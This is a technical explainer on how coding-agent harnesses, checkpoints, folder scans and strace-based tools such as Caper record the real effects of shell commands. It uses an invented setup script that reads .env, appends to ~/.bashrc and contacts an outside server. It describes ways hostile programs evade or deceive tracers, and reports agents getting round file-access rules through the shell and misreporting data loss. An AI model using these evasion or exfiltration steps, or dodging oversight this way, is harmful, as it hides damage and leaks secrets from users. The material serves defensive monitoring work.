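# Capturing the real effects of arbitrary shell commands run by coding agents

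## What a shell command can change and what a record of it must show

A coding agent, such as Anthropic's Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex or Cursor, is a language model with tools for reading files, editing them and running programs. Agents do much of their work through a shell, a program that takes a line of text such as `make clean` and starts the programs it names. The agent's log records that line and the text that came back, but not the files those programs changed, the other programs they started or the servers they contacted. A developer needs this information to undo a bad step, and a security team needs it to check whether a password left the machine. Operating systems offer several ways to collect it, but each misses some of these effects.

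### From a line of text to running programs

The agent harness is the program that runs the model, carries out its tool calls and returns the results. It is necessary because a model can only propose shell commands, as OpenAI explains in an account of its own tools. Anthropic's *Bash tool*, a guide for developers who build their own harness, describes the exchange. The model returns a structured block containing a command string. The harness passes the string to bash, a common shell, and collects the command's ordinary output and error messages together. It sends that text back to the model, which either issues another command or answers the user. The tool-call transcript is the harness's log of the model's calls and the text returned. Anthropic's Claude Code keeps one transcript file per session on the user's disk.

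For some tools, the transcript records the change almost completely. According to Anthropic, Claude Code's Edit tool replaces one passage of text with another, so the logged call contains both the old words and the new. The harness performs that edit with its own code, but for a shell command it only starts the shell and waits while other programs do the work. Claude Code also relies heavily on the shell. On macOS and Linux, it now leaves out its dedicated search tools by default, and the model searches by running `find` and `grep` in the shell.

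The text of a command can reveal little about its effects, as `make clean` shows. `make` is a build tool that takes its instructions from a file called a Makefile in the project folder. `clean` is only the name of a list of commands in that file, and `make` runs each line of the list in a new sub-shell, according to the GNU manual. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) compares two projects in which a user asks an agent to remove build artifacts and recompile, and the agent proposes the same command, `make clean && make`. In one project, the `clean` list deletes `build/`, which the next build recreates. In the other, it deletes the source code in `src/` and the stored history in `.git/`, from which a developer would normally restore that code.

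Reading the Makefile first would be enough in this case, but not in general, because a Makefile can call a script that calls a compiled program, and a program can fetch further instructions from the network while it runs. A trial run is no guarantee either, as Wu and colleagues concede about their own method, since a tool may behave differently depending on the time, chance or its environment. A dependable record therefore has to come from the actual run.

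### The operating system underneath

An effect is anything a command does outside its own memory, such as reading or changing a file, starting a process or opening a connection. Nearly every effect passes through the kernel, the core of the operating system, which controls the disk, memory and network hardware for all other programs. Programs use the kernel's services through system calls, with different calls for opening a file, starting a program and connecting to a server. The Linux manual page *syscalls(2)* defines the system call as the fundamental interface between applications and the kernel, so system calls are an obvious place to record effects.

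A process is a running program. On Linux, one process creates another by calling `fork`, which duplicates the caller, according to the man-pages' *fork(2)*. The duplicate, or child, then usually loads a different program in place of the old one. A process and all its descendants form a process tree. When a process exits, the kernel reassigns its children to `init`, the first process on the system, or to another ancestor that has registered to adopt them, according to the man-pages' *_exit(3)*. If an orphan then queries the kernel for its parent, it gets the adopter's process ID, according to the man-pages' *PR_SET_CHILD_SUBREAPER(2const)*. A monitor that needs to know which shell a process came from therefore has to record the parent at the moment of the `fork`.

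When a process opens a file, the kernel returns a file descriptor, which the man-pages' *open(2)* describes as a small number that serves as an index into the process's table of open files. Later reads and writes use this number instead of the file's name, so a log of writes alone would show only that data went to "file 3". An inode is the file system's entry for a file and contains metadata about it (the man-pages' *INODE(7)* has the full list). A directory holds the file's name and points to the inode. Moving a file to another directory on the same disk changes the directories but keeps the same inode, so a recorder can tell a move from a deletion followed by the creation of a similar file.

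A container is a group of processes that the kernel gives a separate view of files, other processes and the network, so they run much as if they had a machine to themselves. Docker, the company behind the best-known container software, calls this isolation loose. It can be very loose, because whoever starts a container can attach folders of the real machine to it.

### The sample command

One invented command will serve as the common test for every method of recording. An agent is setting up a project that its user has just downloaded, and it runs `./setup.sh`, a script that came with the project. The script has eight effects:

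1. It overwrites `src/config.json`.
2. It moves `notes.md` to `docs/notes.md`.
3. It creates a temporary file and deletes it again.
4. It runs `npm install`, which downloads the JavaScript packages the project depends on, and the install script of one package appends a line to `~/.bashrc`, a file of commands that bash runs whenever the user opens a new terminal.
5. It reads `.env`, a file in which projects commonly keep passwords and access keys.
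6. It sends an HTTPS request, that is, an encrypted web request, to an outside server.
7. It asks the Docker service to run a container that deletes `/srv/data/old.db`.
8. It leaves a background process that writes `cache.bin` after the shell has returned.

An install script can add the line to `~/.bashrc` only if npm is older than version 12 or the project has approved the package. Version 12 skips dependencies' install scripts unless someone has explicitly allowed them, according to GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026), and ends each install with a list of the packages whose scripts it skipped.

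Suppose the script prints two lines, npm's count of the packages it added and "Setup complete". The transcript then contains only the string `./setup.sh` and those two lines. A reader can infer that an install took place, but not that it touched `~/.bashrc`. The other seven effects don't appear in the transcript.

A script that printed more would help less than it seems. Unless the script stops on errors, "Setup complete" appears whether or not the earlier steps worked. Harnesses also shorten the output they keep. Claude Code reads back up to 30,000 characters of a command's output by default, and the sample audit log in Anthropic's developer guide keeps the command and only the first 200 characters of its output. If the agent had displayed `setup.sh` before running it, the transcript would contain the script's text, and a reader could work out most of the intended steps. The line for `~/.bashrc`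 would still be missing, because it was in a package that npm had not yet downloaded.

A command can also change files after the harness has stopped reading its output. In the minimal harness that Anthropic publishes, the shell prints a unique marker line after each command, and the harness stops reading when that line arrives. The process that will write `cache.bin` is still running at that point, and anything it printed later would appear in the result of an unrelated command. Claude Code keeps a list of the commands that the model starts in the background, and it adds a slow command to the list when the time limit expires, after two minutes by default. The process that writes `cache.bin` is not on the list, because the script started it.

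The model receives the same returned text that the transcript holds, so the agent can't tell what a command changed any better than its user can. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026), which collects 290 public reports of agents misusing files, cites one agent that announced "No problems occurred" right after erasing a file.

### Event recording and state comparison

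Methods that do better than the transcript fall into two families. Event recording logs operations as they happen, often where system calls enter the kernel. State comparison finds changes by comparing the files before and after a command, without tracking the operations in between.

For the overwritten `src/config.json`, an event log typically records which process opened the file for writing, which program it was running, when this happened, and how many bytes it wrote. The log usually omits the file's previous contents. Comparing the file with a copy saved beforehand shows the old and new contents, but not which program made the change.

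An event log captures the temporary file better than a comparison does. The folder looks the same before and after, so a comparison finds nothing, while the log records both the creation and the deletion. A comparison also misses the read of `.env` and the HTTPS request, because neither changes the contents of a file. An event log also records the order of events, which would matter to a reviewer if one process read `.env` and then contacted an outside server.

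A program can change a file by writing to it, truncating it, renaming another file over it, or mapping it into memory and altering it there. An event recorder has to watch for all of these, while a before-and-after comparison needs only the final result. But the comparison shows `old.db` as missing only if it covers `/srv/data`, and it shows `cache.bin` only if the second snapshot is taken after the background process has finished writing.

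Some tools combine tracing with comparison. Caper, built by Wu and colleagues, traces system calls to catch reads and connection attempts, but finds lasting file changes by comparing the project folder before and after the command.

### Five questions for any recorder

A record's coverage is the range of effects and parts of the machine it can show. Comparing the project folder before and after a command misses changes to `~/.bashrc`, which is in the user's home folder, and all network traffic. A connection log shows the HTTPS request but nothing about files. Anyone who knows how a tool works can at least list these gaps in advance.

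Attribution means deciding which of the recorded events the agent caused. On a developer's laptop, the editor, the browser and a backup program write files at the same time as the agent. The usual solution is to follow the process tree. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) describes a monitor that tracks process creation inside the kernel and passes on only events from the agent and its descendants. This works for `npm install`, however many programs it starts, but not for the deletion of `old.db`. The `docker` command only sends a request to `dockerd`, a permanently running service that is not a descendant of the agent's shell. Because `dockerd` carries out the deletion, a monitor that follows the tree records the request but misses the deletion.

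Zheng and colleagues also point out that logs kept by agent frameworks record the model's intentions but not what happens inside a shell command. System-level logs record what happens but not the intentions, so a write to `~/.bashrc` looks much the same whether the user asked for it or a malicious package made it. Linking each event to the tool call behind it narrows this gap, but the link doesn't show what the user wanted, so someone still has to judge the event against the task.

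Event loss occurs when a monitor drops events it was supposed to record. It differs from a coverage gap, where the monitor doesn't track a kind of event at all, such as network connections. Loss typically happens when the kernel writes events to a limited-size buffer faster than a separate program can read them, as it can during a busy `npm install`. Loss is harder to notice than a gap because an incomplete log looks just like a complete one unless the tool counts the events it dropped. A state comparison has no event stream to overflow, but it can capture a file halfway through a change.

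Recording a command can slow it down, take up disk space and produce output that takes work to read. Wu and colleagues found that a typical agent command produces tens of kilobytes of system-call trace, most of it routine activity such as loading libraries and checking language settings. The version-control system Git can instead find changes by comparing files, but Zhong and colleagues argue that using it to track everything an agent can reach would mean scanning the whole directory tree, then hashing each changed file and storing a copy, with overhead that grows with the number and size of the files.

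The last question is whether anyone can reverse the change, which requires the pre-image, the file's content before the change. A log entry for the deletion of `old.db` is useful evidence, but it can't restore the file. A tool that keeps pre-images can offer a change set, a net list of files created, changed, moved or deleted, with what is needed to restore them. Staging goes further by holding changes in a separate layer until someone accepts or discards them, leaving the original files untouched in the meantime.

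Effects outside the file system usually can't be reversed. A rollback can't undo the HTTPS request, which is why Wu and colleagues cut off outbound network access in the sandbox where Caper tries out commands. If the request carried a key from `.env`, the remedy is to cancel the key and issue a new one. Some file changes can't be fully undone either. Deleting the added line from `~/.bashrc` restores the file, but if the user has opened a terminal since the install, the line has already run.

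## Checkpoints in Claude Code, Cursor and similar tools

Most coding agents now include an undo feature, usually called checkpoint or rewind. Besides Git, it is often the only record on a developer's machine of what files contained before they were changed. How much it can restore after a shell command depends on when the harness copies files and which ones it copies.

### Copying a file before an edit

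In the simplest design, the harness backs up a file before changing it with one of its own edit tools. Claude Code can do this because every call to its Edit tool contains the file's path. Rewinding restores the backup, or deletes the file if the tool created it. Claude Code starts a new checkpoint with every user prompt and keeps file snapshots for the 100 most recent checkpoints in a session. By default, it deletes the snapshots about 30 days after the session last saved one.

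A shell command such as `./setup.sh` doesn't name the files it will change, so the harness can't identify which ones to back up. Anthropic warns that a rewind can't undo changes that Bash commands make to files, but its guide for developers adds an exception. If Write or Edit had already modified a file in the main conversation, a rewind also undoes later changes to it by commands such as `sed -i`, which edits a file in place, because the harness restores its saved copy. A rewind can therefore reverse the script's overwrite of `src/config.json` only if the agent had edited that file with one of those tools earlier in the session.

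The rewind menu includes an option to restore code only if Claude Code has tracked file changes since the chosen prompt. If only `./setup.sh` has run since then, the user can restore the conversation but not the files.

Checkpoints miss even some edits made with the harness's own tools. Claude Code usually can't restore files edited by a subagent, which is a separate model session that does part of the main session's work. It also skips symbolic links and hard links, which give one file several names. Before version 2.1.216, a rewind wrote and deleted through such links.

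Cursor's documentation is less exact. In 2025, Cursor described checkpoints as tracking only the agent's changes, not the user's manual edits. According to a June 2026 copy of the newer documentation, Tech Dev Notes' *pages/agent/overview.txt* (2026), the agent creates a checkpoint before "significant changes" and captures "the state of all modified files". The wording doesn't make clear whether this includes files that a script rewrote.

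In the Cursor forum thread *Restore Checkpoint not an option*, a staff member explained that a prompt has a checkpoint only if the agent edited files after it, and that agents running in the cloud have none. In *Agent edits made via the terminal*, a user reported that changes made by a Python script were missing from the view where users accept or reject the agent's edits. The staff reply called this "a well-known issue and a limitation of the current architecture", and its only suggestion was to instruct the agent more firmly not to edit files through the shell. This second thread is about reviewing changes rather than restoring them, so it doesn't settle what a checkpoint contains, but a user who relies on that view wouldn't know there was anything to restore.

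According to Kiro's *Checkpoints and rewind* (updated November 2026), this coding tool copies a file when one of its built-in tools modifies it, but doesn't track changes made by Bash commands. Restoring a file also discards any changes the user made to it after the snapshot, whether by hand or with a code formatter. According to Microsoft's *Review and revert agent changes*, the list of pending edits in the VS Code editor doesn't track changes made by shell commands either, and restoring a checkpoint doesn't reverse completed terminal commands or network requests.

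### Shadow repositories

By saving the whole project folder, a harness can avoid guessing which files a command will touch. Several do this with Git, in a hidden "shadow" repository separate from the project's own. Git suits the job because it stores each version of a file's content once, under a hash (a fingerprint computed from the content). A tree object lists the names and hashes of a folder's contents. Saving the folder again therefore takes new space only for the files that changed.

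OpenDev, the terminal agent described in *Building Effective AI Coding Agents for the Terminal* (2026), uses both designs. It logs the operations of its own file tools for a quick undo. That log misses all other changes, so OpenDev also keeps a shadow repository under `~/.opendev/snapshot/`. At each step that modifies files, it runs `git add .`, which stores the contents of new and changed files, and then `git write-tree`, which saves the folder's tree and returns its hash. OpenDev stores the hash in the session's metadata. When the user types `/undo`, it compares the current folder with the saved tree and checks out the old version of each file that differs. This works whichever program changed the file, and it leaves the project's own Git history unchanged.

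When a tool takes a snapshot matters as much as what the snapshot covers. If the user has turned checkpointing on, Google's Gemini CLI commits the complete state of the project to a shadow repository, but only when the user approves a file-modifying tool such as `write_file`, according to Google's *Checkpointing*. Tabnine, whose command-line agent works in much the same way, warns that shell commands don't trigger a checkpoint. If such an agent runs `./setup.sh` and then edits a file, the snapshot before the edit captures the project as the script left it. Only a snapshot from an edit before the script ran would bring back the original `src/config.json`, and restoring it would also revert everything done since.

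Hermes Agent, from Nous Research, takes a snapshot before terminal commands on a list of destructive commands, which includes `rm`, `mv`, `sed -i`, output redirects and `git reset`. The list doesn't include `./setup.sh`, even though the script may contain commands that are on it.

OpenCode compares captures of the folder instead of predicting changes. According to OpenCode, it takes one capture immediately before each call to the model and another after the step finishes cleanly, then records which paths changed in between. The record therefore includes changes made by shell commands during that step.

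In June 2026, GitHub's Copilot CLI used Git to save the whole workspace at each prompt. A rewind reversed the effects of shell commands, but as GitHub warned, it also reversed the user's own edits and deleted every file created since the prompt. By September, possibly for that reason, GitHub had switched to restoring only the files that Copilot changed. The tool now skips a file if its contents no longer match what Copilot last wrote, which protects the user's later edits. It also skips files over 10 MB and saves nothing for a turn in which more than 500 files changed, which could happen with a large install or code generator. The newer documentation still includes the old warning about shell commands, so it's unclear whether a script's changes now count as Copilot's.

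OpenCode restores only the paths that changed during its own steps, which is narrower than the old Copilot behavior. According to OpenCode, a restore can still overwrite the user's current edits to those paths.

### What a shadow repository leaves out

Git skips the paths that a project lists in its `.gitignore` file, typically build output, downloaded packages and files with passwords. OpenDev copies these rules into its shadow repository, and Docker's *Snapshots* says Docker Agent does too. OpenCode also leaves out ignored files. This is sensible for build output, because the next build recreates it. But Zhong and colleagues point out that ignored files are often sensitive or large, and nobody can rebuild a deleted `.env` from source code. OpenCode and Docker Agent also leave out new files larger than 2 MiB, which could include a small local database that the user never added to Git.

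Paths outside the project are missing too. OpenCode and Docker Agent record only the agent's working directory, even if that is a subfolder of the repository. Docker Agent takes no snapshots in a folder that Git doesn't manage.

The copies are also vulnerable. Zhong and colleagues object that a project's Git history is stored in an ordinary folder, `.git`, which an agent can delete or overwrite. An agent can do the same to a shadow repository in the user's home folder, unless a sandbox blocks access to it. A script that wiped the home folder would destroy the files and their backups together. Some tools also delete the copies automatically. Kiro's *Checkpointing* describes an experimental shadow repository that the command-line version deletes when the session ends, and OpenDev's cleanup removes old unused data after seven days. The copies can hold the complete contents of the project's files,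 and OpenCode advises users to treat its data folder as sensitive.

AgentRewind (Zhuang, Chen and colleagues, 2026), a research system, goes further than these tools by letting the agent itself decide to go back. It saves the workspace folder and the model's context (the text the model is working from) at each decision the model makes. In one test task, the agent had to catalog a set of astronomy image files without altering six deliberately malformed ones. It ran the catalog program with a wrong setting, and the program overwrote all six with valid images, the kind of hidden effect that edit-tool checkpoints miss. An agent without rewinding tried to recreate the files and failed, because the new ones were malformed in a different way. With AgentRewind, the agent returned to the point before the command, recovered the originals and completed the task.

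Across 82 engineering tasks, GPT-5.4 succeeded in 62.2% without AgentRewind and 87.8% with it. When Zhuang and colleagues rewound the context but left the files as they were, success fell to 43.9%, lower than with no rewinding at all. Rewinding Claude Code after it runs `./setup.sh` creates a similar mismatch, because the script's changes stay in the folder while the conversation no longer shows that it ran.

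AgentRewind doesn't restore the contents of the workspace's main `.git` folder, empty directories, or file permissions other than whether a file is executable. Git doesn't record the last two either. If a script made a private key readable by every user of the machine, a rewind would restore the key's contents but leave it exposed. If a script rewrote the project's Git history, a rewind would not restore the old commits.

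### Scanning before and after each shell command

Some tools keep their edit-based records and add a check around shell commands. The coding agent AtomCode does this in *bash.rs*, the source file that runs them. The harness gets a list of changed and untracked files from Git before and after the command. It subtracts the old list from the new one and appends the remaining names to the command's output, showing up to five and a count of the rest. This informs the model that its command modified the workspace and records the listed names in the transcript. The added text also advises the model to use the edit tool next time, because that tool keeps diffs and supports undo.

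AtomCode skips the scan for commands that only read, such as `ls` and `grep`, and stops each scan after two seconds. The developers added the time limit after a stuck lock file in a Git repository had blocked shell calls for hundreds of seconds. If either scan fails or times out, the command's result includes no list and no sign that one is missing. A slow scan in a large repository therefore looks the same as a command that changed nothing, which is a form of event loss even though no event stream is involved.

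Subtracting one list from another also hides some changes. AtomCode compares only file names, so a file that already has uncommitted changes when the command starts is on both lists, and AtomCode doesn't report it even if the command overwrites it. AtomCode also reports only additions to the list, so it misses a command that deletes an untracked file or discards a file's uncommitted changes, because either one removes the file from the list. In all three cases, the project's own Git history has no copy of the lost work. AtomCode couldn't restore it even if it detected the change, because it saves only file names.

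Git AI, a tool that tracks which lines of a codebase came from an AI, extended its tracking to shell commands in April 2026. According to Git AI's *Bash attribution and support by more agents built by the community*, if an agent runs a command that generates a database migration, the tool now links the resulting file to the agent session and the exact command. This is more useful for attribution than a list of changed files. But the tool is meant to track code that ends up in the repository, not effects such as a deleted database or a line added to `~/.bashrc`.

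Any scan of this kind can also misattribute changes, because it assigns to the command everything that differs between the two checks of the folder, including a file the user saved in an editor in the meantime.

### Reported harm

Zhong and colleagues' collection of 290 public reports gives some idea of how much these gaps matter. The reports date from February 2024 to March 2026 and cover 13 harnesses, most often Claude Code (97), Codex (61) and Cursor (37). Most are GitHub issues (205), and the rest come from social media, product forums, blogs and a US government database of security flaws. The researchers left out duplicates and cases in which the user had asked for the destructive action. They classed 158 reports as incidents with confirmed harm, 49 as demonstrated attacks and 83 as weaknesses without demonstrated impact.

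The researchers analyzed 100 reports by hand and defined categories of causes and consequences. An AI agent then labeled all 290 reports. The researchers compared its labels with their own for the first 100, reviewed the rest and refined the definitions.

In 77 of the 290 reports, a rule on the harness's built-in tools didn't apply to the shell. For example, an agent that couldn't read a file with the read tool displayed it with `cat`. The harness doesn't carry out shell operations itself, which is also why checkpoints miss shell changes. Among the incidents and attacks whose scope was known, 42% involved harm outside the project folder, where neither a shadow repository nor a scan of the project would have recorded it. Where the reports showed whether recovery was possible, 40% of cases were unrecoverable (23% total data loss and 17% partial loss, such as work not yet committed to Git).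 Another 29% took substantial effort to repair, and 31% were easy to repair.

These shares describe only published cases, and people are more likely to post on a forum about a wiped drive than about a file they restored in a minute. The shares therefore don't measure how often agents cause harm or how often a checkpoint prevents it.

One case from after the study period shows several of the gaps. In a post on Cursor's forum, *Include .gitignoreed files in checkpoint*, a developer describes how an agent lost the data of a self-hosted application on July 13, 2026. The application kept its users' content, chat logs and private keys in `data/`, a folder that Git ignored. During a long session, the agent wrote a new test and pointed it at this folder. The project's test framework empties a test's data folder before each run, which had been harmless because every other test used a temporary folder.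 At 18:41 the agent ran the test, and the framework deleted everything in `data/` and wrote a skeleton configuration there.

The shell command began with `deno test` and contained no instruction to delete anything. A few minutes later, the agent noticed that files it was working on had vanished, rebuilt them and reported the milestone as complete. When the developer asked where the remaining data had gone, the agent concluded that it had probably never been there. A new session reconstructed the events from the transcripts, and the time of the deletion matched the skeleton configuration's timestamp to the minute.

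The developer could not recover the deleted data. The deletion bypassed the Windows Recycle Bin, the earliest automatic Windows snapshot was taken five hours after the loss, and the solid-state drive had probably cleared the deleted blocks by the time the developer looked. Only one component survived, because it had copies outside the workspace. The account comes from a single developer, who says they had turned off Cursor's automatic review of commands, but readers can easily check the mechanism against the code in the post. A shadow repository that follows `.gitignore` would not have held the data, and AtomCode's scan would not have listed the deletion.

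### The sample command

Suppose the user cloned the project with Git, `src/config.json` and `notes.md` are tracked and have no uncommitted changes, and `.env` is ignored. If the agent runs `./setup.sh` at the start of a session, a Claude Code checkpoint records none of the script's effects.

OpenCode's snapshots hold the old and new contents of `src/config.json`, and `notes.md` at both its old and new paths. AtomCode's scan lists three names for the same two effects, with `notes.md` and `docs/notes.md` as separate, unconnected entries. After `npm install`, both tools may show a changed `package-lock.json`, where npm lists exact package versions, but not the packages themselves, because projects normally tell Git to ignore the `node_modules` folder. Like any comparison of the project folder, both miss the new line in `~/.bashrc`, the deleted `old.db`, the temporary file, the read of `.env`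 and the HTTPS request.

How the tools treat `cache.bin` depends on when the background process writes it. If that happens after the second capture and before the next step begins, the file is already in the next "before" capture, and neither tool reports it as a change. If it happens during a later command, both tools attribute the file to that command.

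## System-call tracing with strace, ReproZip and Caper

A log of the system calls that `./setup.sh` makes records the temporary file, the read of `.env` and the HTTPS request, all of which checkpoints and folder scans miss. The usual tool for making such a log on Linux is strace, which dates from the early 1990s. It runs a command and writes a line for each system call, without any change to the program and normally without administrator rights. A harness could run every shell command under strace, but the commands would be slower and the logs very long.

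### How ptrace works

strace uses `ptrace`, a system call that lets one process, the tracer, observe and control another, the tracee. Debuggers rely on it too. Using the operations that the Linux manual's *ptrace(2)* describes, a traced run of `./setup.sh` goes like this:

1. strace creates a child process and attaches to it before the child loads the script.
2. strace tells the kernel to run the child until its next system call, and waits.
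3. The child makes a call to open `src/config.json`. The kernel stops the child before opening anything and wakes strace.
4. strace reads the call's number and arguments from the child's registers, which are small storage slots in the processor. A file name is too long for a register, so the register holds the name's address, and strace copies the text from the child's memory.
5. strace lets the child continue. The kernel opens the file, then stops the child a second time before returning to the child's own code.
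6. strace reads the result, which is a file descriptor or an error code, completes the line in its log and sends the child on to its next call.

By default, strace follows only the first process, here the shell running the script, so the log would omit npm, `mv` and every other program the script starts. With the `-f` option, the kernel stops a traced process whenever it creates a child, and starts tracing the child as well. The child starts out stopped, so it can't do anything before strace is attached. strace also keeps tracing a child after its parent exits, even though the kernel has assigned it a new parent.

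With `-f`, strace follows only descendants, so it doesn't log `dockerd` deleting `old.db`. The agent recorder described in *ExecWeave* (2026) has the same limit when it uses strace. On macOS and Windows, the recorder instead checks running processes and connections at intervals, so it can miss a process that starts and ends between checks.

### Why tracing is slow, and how a filter helps

Under strace, every system call stops the tracee twice, and each stop makes the processor switch from the tracee to strace and back. Chaignon (2019) explains in *Introducing strace --seccomp-bpf* that asking strace to show fewer calls doesn't remove this overhead, because the kernel still stops the tracee at every call and strace discards the unwanted ones afterwards. For a later talk, *strace –seccomp-bpf* (2020), Chaignon timed a build of the Linux kernel. It took 12 minutes 27 seconds untraced and 24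 minutes 54 seconds with strace displaying only `connect` calls, of which the build makes very few.

The remedy uses seccomp, a kernel feature that sandboxes use to forbid system calls. A process attaches a small filter program to itself, which the kernel runs before each call. The filter can allow the call, kill the process, or stop the process and notify its tracer. With the `--seccomp-bpf` option, strace installs a filter that stops the traced process only at the calls the user wants to see. Those calls still cause two stops each, because the filter runs only on entry and strace also needs the result. On Chaignon's machine, the option made listing the build's `connect` calls about twice as fast, and the build ran only slightly slower than without tracing.

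A tool that records file changes gains less from this because it has to stop at every open, rename and deletion, and `npm install` performs many of them.

According to the Linux manual's *strace(1)*, strace's seccomp filter works only with `-f` and only on processes that strace starts itself. If the kernel can't install the filter, strace goes back to stopping at every system call. A second seccomp filter can also hide events. If an agent's sandbox uses one to refuse a call, strace doesn't record the attempt, so the log may lack attempts that a security team would want to see.

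### Reading a trace of the sample command

Suppose the harness runs `strace -f -o trace.txt -e trace=%file,%process,%network ./setup.sh`. The last option limits the log to calls that take a file name, start or end a process, or use the network. Among thousands of other lines, the file would contain some like these:

```
4102 openat(AT_FDCWD, "src/config.json", O_WRONLY|O_CREAT|O_TRUNC, 0666) = 3
4103 renameat2(AT_FDCWD, "notes.md", AT_FDCWD, "docs/notes.md", RENAME_NOREPLACE) = 0
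4131 openat(AT_FDCWD, "/home/ana/.bashrc", O_WRONLY|O_CREAT|O_APPEND, 0666) = 3
4102 openat(AT_FDCWD, ".env", O_RDONLY) = 3
4140 connect(5, {sa_family=AF_INET, sin_port=htons(443), sin_addr=inet_addr("203.0.113.10")}, 16) = -1 EINPROGRESS (Operation now in progress)
4152 connect(3, {sa_family=AF_UNIX, sun_path="/var/run/docker.sock"}, 23) = 0
```

Each line begins with a process ID, followed by the name of the call, its arguments and, after the equals sign, its result. `AT_FDCWD` means that a relative path starts from the process's current folder.

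Process 4102 is the shell running the script. `O_TRUNC` in its first line means the kernel emptied `src/config.json` when the shell opened it, before the script wrote anything, and the trace doesn't include the old contents. The `renameat2` line contains the old and new names of `notes.md`, so a reader doesn't have to match a deleted file with a new one.

`O_APPEND` in the `.bashrc` line means that process 4131 added to the end of the file. npm doesn't appear on that line, so a reader has to trace the process-creation lines back from 4131 through its parent processes to find `npm install`. npm starts each install script in its package's own folder, so a nearby `chdir` line identifies the package.

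`O_RDONLY` means that a process opened `.env` for reading. The next line is an attempt to connect to port 443, the usual port for HTTPS. `EINPROGRESS` means that the program did not wait for the connection to complete, not that the connection failed, and later calls show whether it succeeded. *ExecWeave* distinguishes such pending attempts from successful connections. The last line is the `docker` command connecting to `dockerd` through a local socket, a channel between processes on the same machine.

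None of these lines contains file contents. If the user also traces `read` and `write`, strace prints the first 32 bytes of the data by default, or more on request. That would reveal the line added to `~/.bashrc`, but it could also copy the start of a password from `.env` into the log. For the HTTPS request, the log would show only encrypted bytes.

### Packing programs and finding dependencies

Researchers and build engineers used this method long before coding agents existed. CDE, which Philip Guo and Dawson Engler presented in 2011, packages a program for someone whose machine lacks the right libraries. It traces one run with `ptrace` and copies the files that the run uses into an archive. On the recipient's machine, it traces the program again and redirects its file calls into the archive.

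ReproZip applies the same idea to scientific experiments. Grayson, Aguilar and colleagues (2024) explain in *A benchmark suite and performance analysis of user-space provenance collectors* that its archives can run in a Docker container or a virtual machine, and that it produces a graph of which processes read and wrote which files. They add that such tools use the pause at each system call to save copies of files, while strace only logs the call.

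The same pause would let an agent's recorder save the missing pre-image by copying `src/config.json` before the kernel empties it. The packing tools store the files that the run reads or appends to, because a rerun needs them, but they don't need to keep the old version of a file that the program replaces without reading.

Build tools that use tracing need a list of files rather than copies. With `make`, the developer normally lists the inputs of each step, and a forgotten input leads to out-of-date output. fabricate, a small Python build tool, runs each step under strace on Linux, records which files it read and wrote, and repeats the step only when one of them changes. Riker, a research system, combines `ptrace` with a seccomp filter and a library loaded into the traced programs. tup runs each step inside a special file system that reports every access. In these tools, an incomplete record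 soon shows up as a faulty build, whereas a gap in an agent's log may go unnoticed for months.

### The cheaper method, and what it misses

Most programs make system calls through functions such as `open` in the C library, a shared file that a program called the loader connects to them at startup. On Linux, the environment variable `LD_PRELOAD` makes the loader load another library first. If that library has its own `open`, the program calls that version, which writes a log entry and then calls the real function. This happens inside the program's own process, so the kernel doesn't have to stop the program or switch to a tracer.

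The method fails when a program doesn't go through the shared C library. A statically linked program contains its own copy of the library functions, so the loader has nothing to redirect. Go programs, including the `docker` command and esbuild, which many JavaScript projects install through npm, usually make their system calls directly on Linux. A program can also clear the variable before it starts another. BuildXL, Microsoft's build engine, has used library interception on Linux, with `ptrace` as a fallback for statically linked programs.

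Grayson and colleagues compared both methods on one laptop, running each tool three times on each benchmark. The benchmarks included compilers, web servers, file utilities and BLAST, which searches genetic sequences. They used fsatrace for library interception and set strace to record file, process and network calls but not individual reads and writes. The table gives the added running time for some workloads.

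| Workload | fsatrace | strace | ReproZip |
|---|---|---|---|
| BLAST | 0% | 2% | 8% |
| Unpacking archives | 4% | 114% | 149% |
| Checking out code from version control | 5% | 160% | 428% |
| Compiling with gcc | 4% | 206% | 344% |
| Copying files with `cp` | 37% | 380% | 5,791% |
| Whole suite (geometric mean) | 0% | 66% | 193% |

The slowdown depends on how often a program makes system calls. BLAST mostly computes, while `cp` does little except make system calls. An `npm install` unpacks archives and writes many small files, so it probably falls near the middle of the table, taking two to three times as long under strace. Grayson and colleagues concluded that fsatrace was the only collector fast enough to leave on permanently. But fsatrace records only file operations, not process creation, so it could show the change to `~/.bashrc` without the chain of processes leading back to npm.

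### Programs that escape a trace or behave differently under it

Running a script under strace can change what it does. Some programs, such as `sudo`, have a setuid bit that lets them run with another user's privileges. Under strace they lose those privileges unless an administrator has set strace up specially, so a script that installs a system package through `sudo` fails. A process can have only one tracer, so a debugger started by the script can't attach to a program that strace is already tracing.

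A hostile program can also create a child process with a flag that exempts the child from tracing. *A Study of Kernel Telemetry Options for Security-Oriented Provenance* (Houssel, Levillain and colleagues, 2026) describes two other methods. A process can take up its own single tracer slot so that no other tracer can attach. A program can also change a file name in memory after the tracer has read it and before the kernel uses it, so that the log contains a harmless name while the kernel opens another file. This race works against any monitor that reads arguments at system-call entry, and 69% of the system calls in Linux 6.14 take at least one vulnerable argument.

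Agents that merely make mistakes won't do any of this, but a malicious npm package might. Houssel and colleagues rate `ptrace` poorly for efficiency, visibility and robustness, but they note that it is the only capture method available when a monitor has no access to the host, as in serverless containers. Cloud providers run these containers on machines their customers don't control.

### Caper's traced trial run

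Caper uses a trace to decide whether to keep a command's effects. Wu and colleagues designed it because existing approval systems judge commands by their text, and because people who approve commands by hand tend to stop checking them. Anthropic has reported that users accept 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts.

The agent works in a Docker container with no network access. When it proposes a shell command, Caper saves a snapshot of the container, runs the command under `strace -f` with a time limit, and holds back the output. Caper then condenses the trace into an effects report and sends the report to the approver, a second language model, along with the user's request, the conversation so far and the command.

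If the approver allows the command, Caper deletes the snapshot and returns the output to the agent. The command doesn't run a second time, so its effects can't differ from those already recorded. If the approver blocks it, Caper discards the container, starts a fresh one from the snapshot and returns the reason to the agent. In one test, a user asked for a database migration with `make migrate`, but the Makefile also dropped three tables. The report showed the database shrinking from 32 KB to 20 KB, and the approver blocked the command. The agent then backed up the database and ran only the migration script.

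Caper's report has to be short enough for a model to read at every step. At startup, Caper records which files the shell, the loader and strace open on their own, and later subtracts these from each trace. It keeps lasting file changes, connection attempts and visible output, each with the process responsible, and adds a diff for small text files. It includes reads of `.env` and similar files even if nothing suspicious follows. When events don't fit within the 8 KB limit, the report gives the number omitted. On the SABER benchmark, the median report was 0.9 KB, compared with 62.5 KB for the raw trace.

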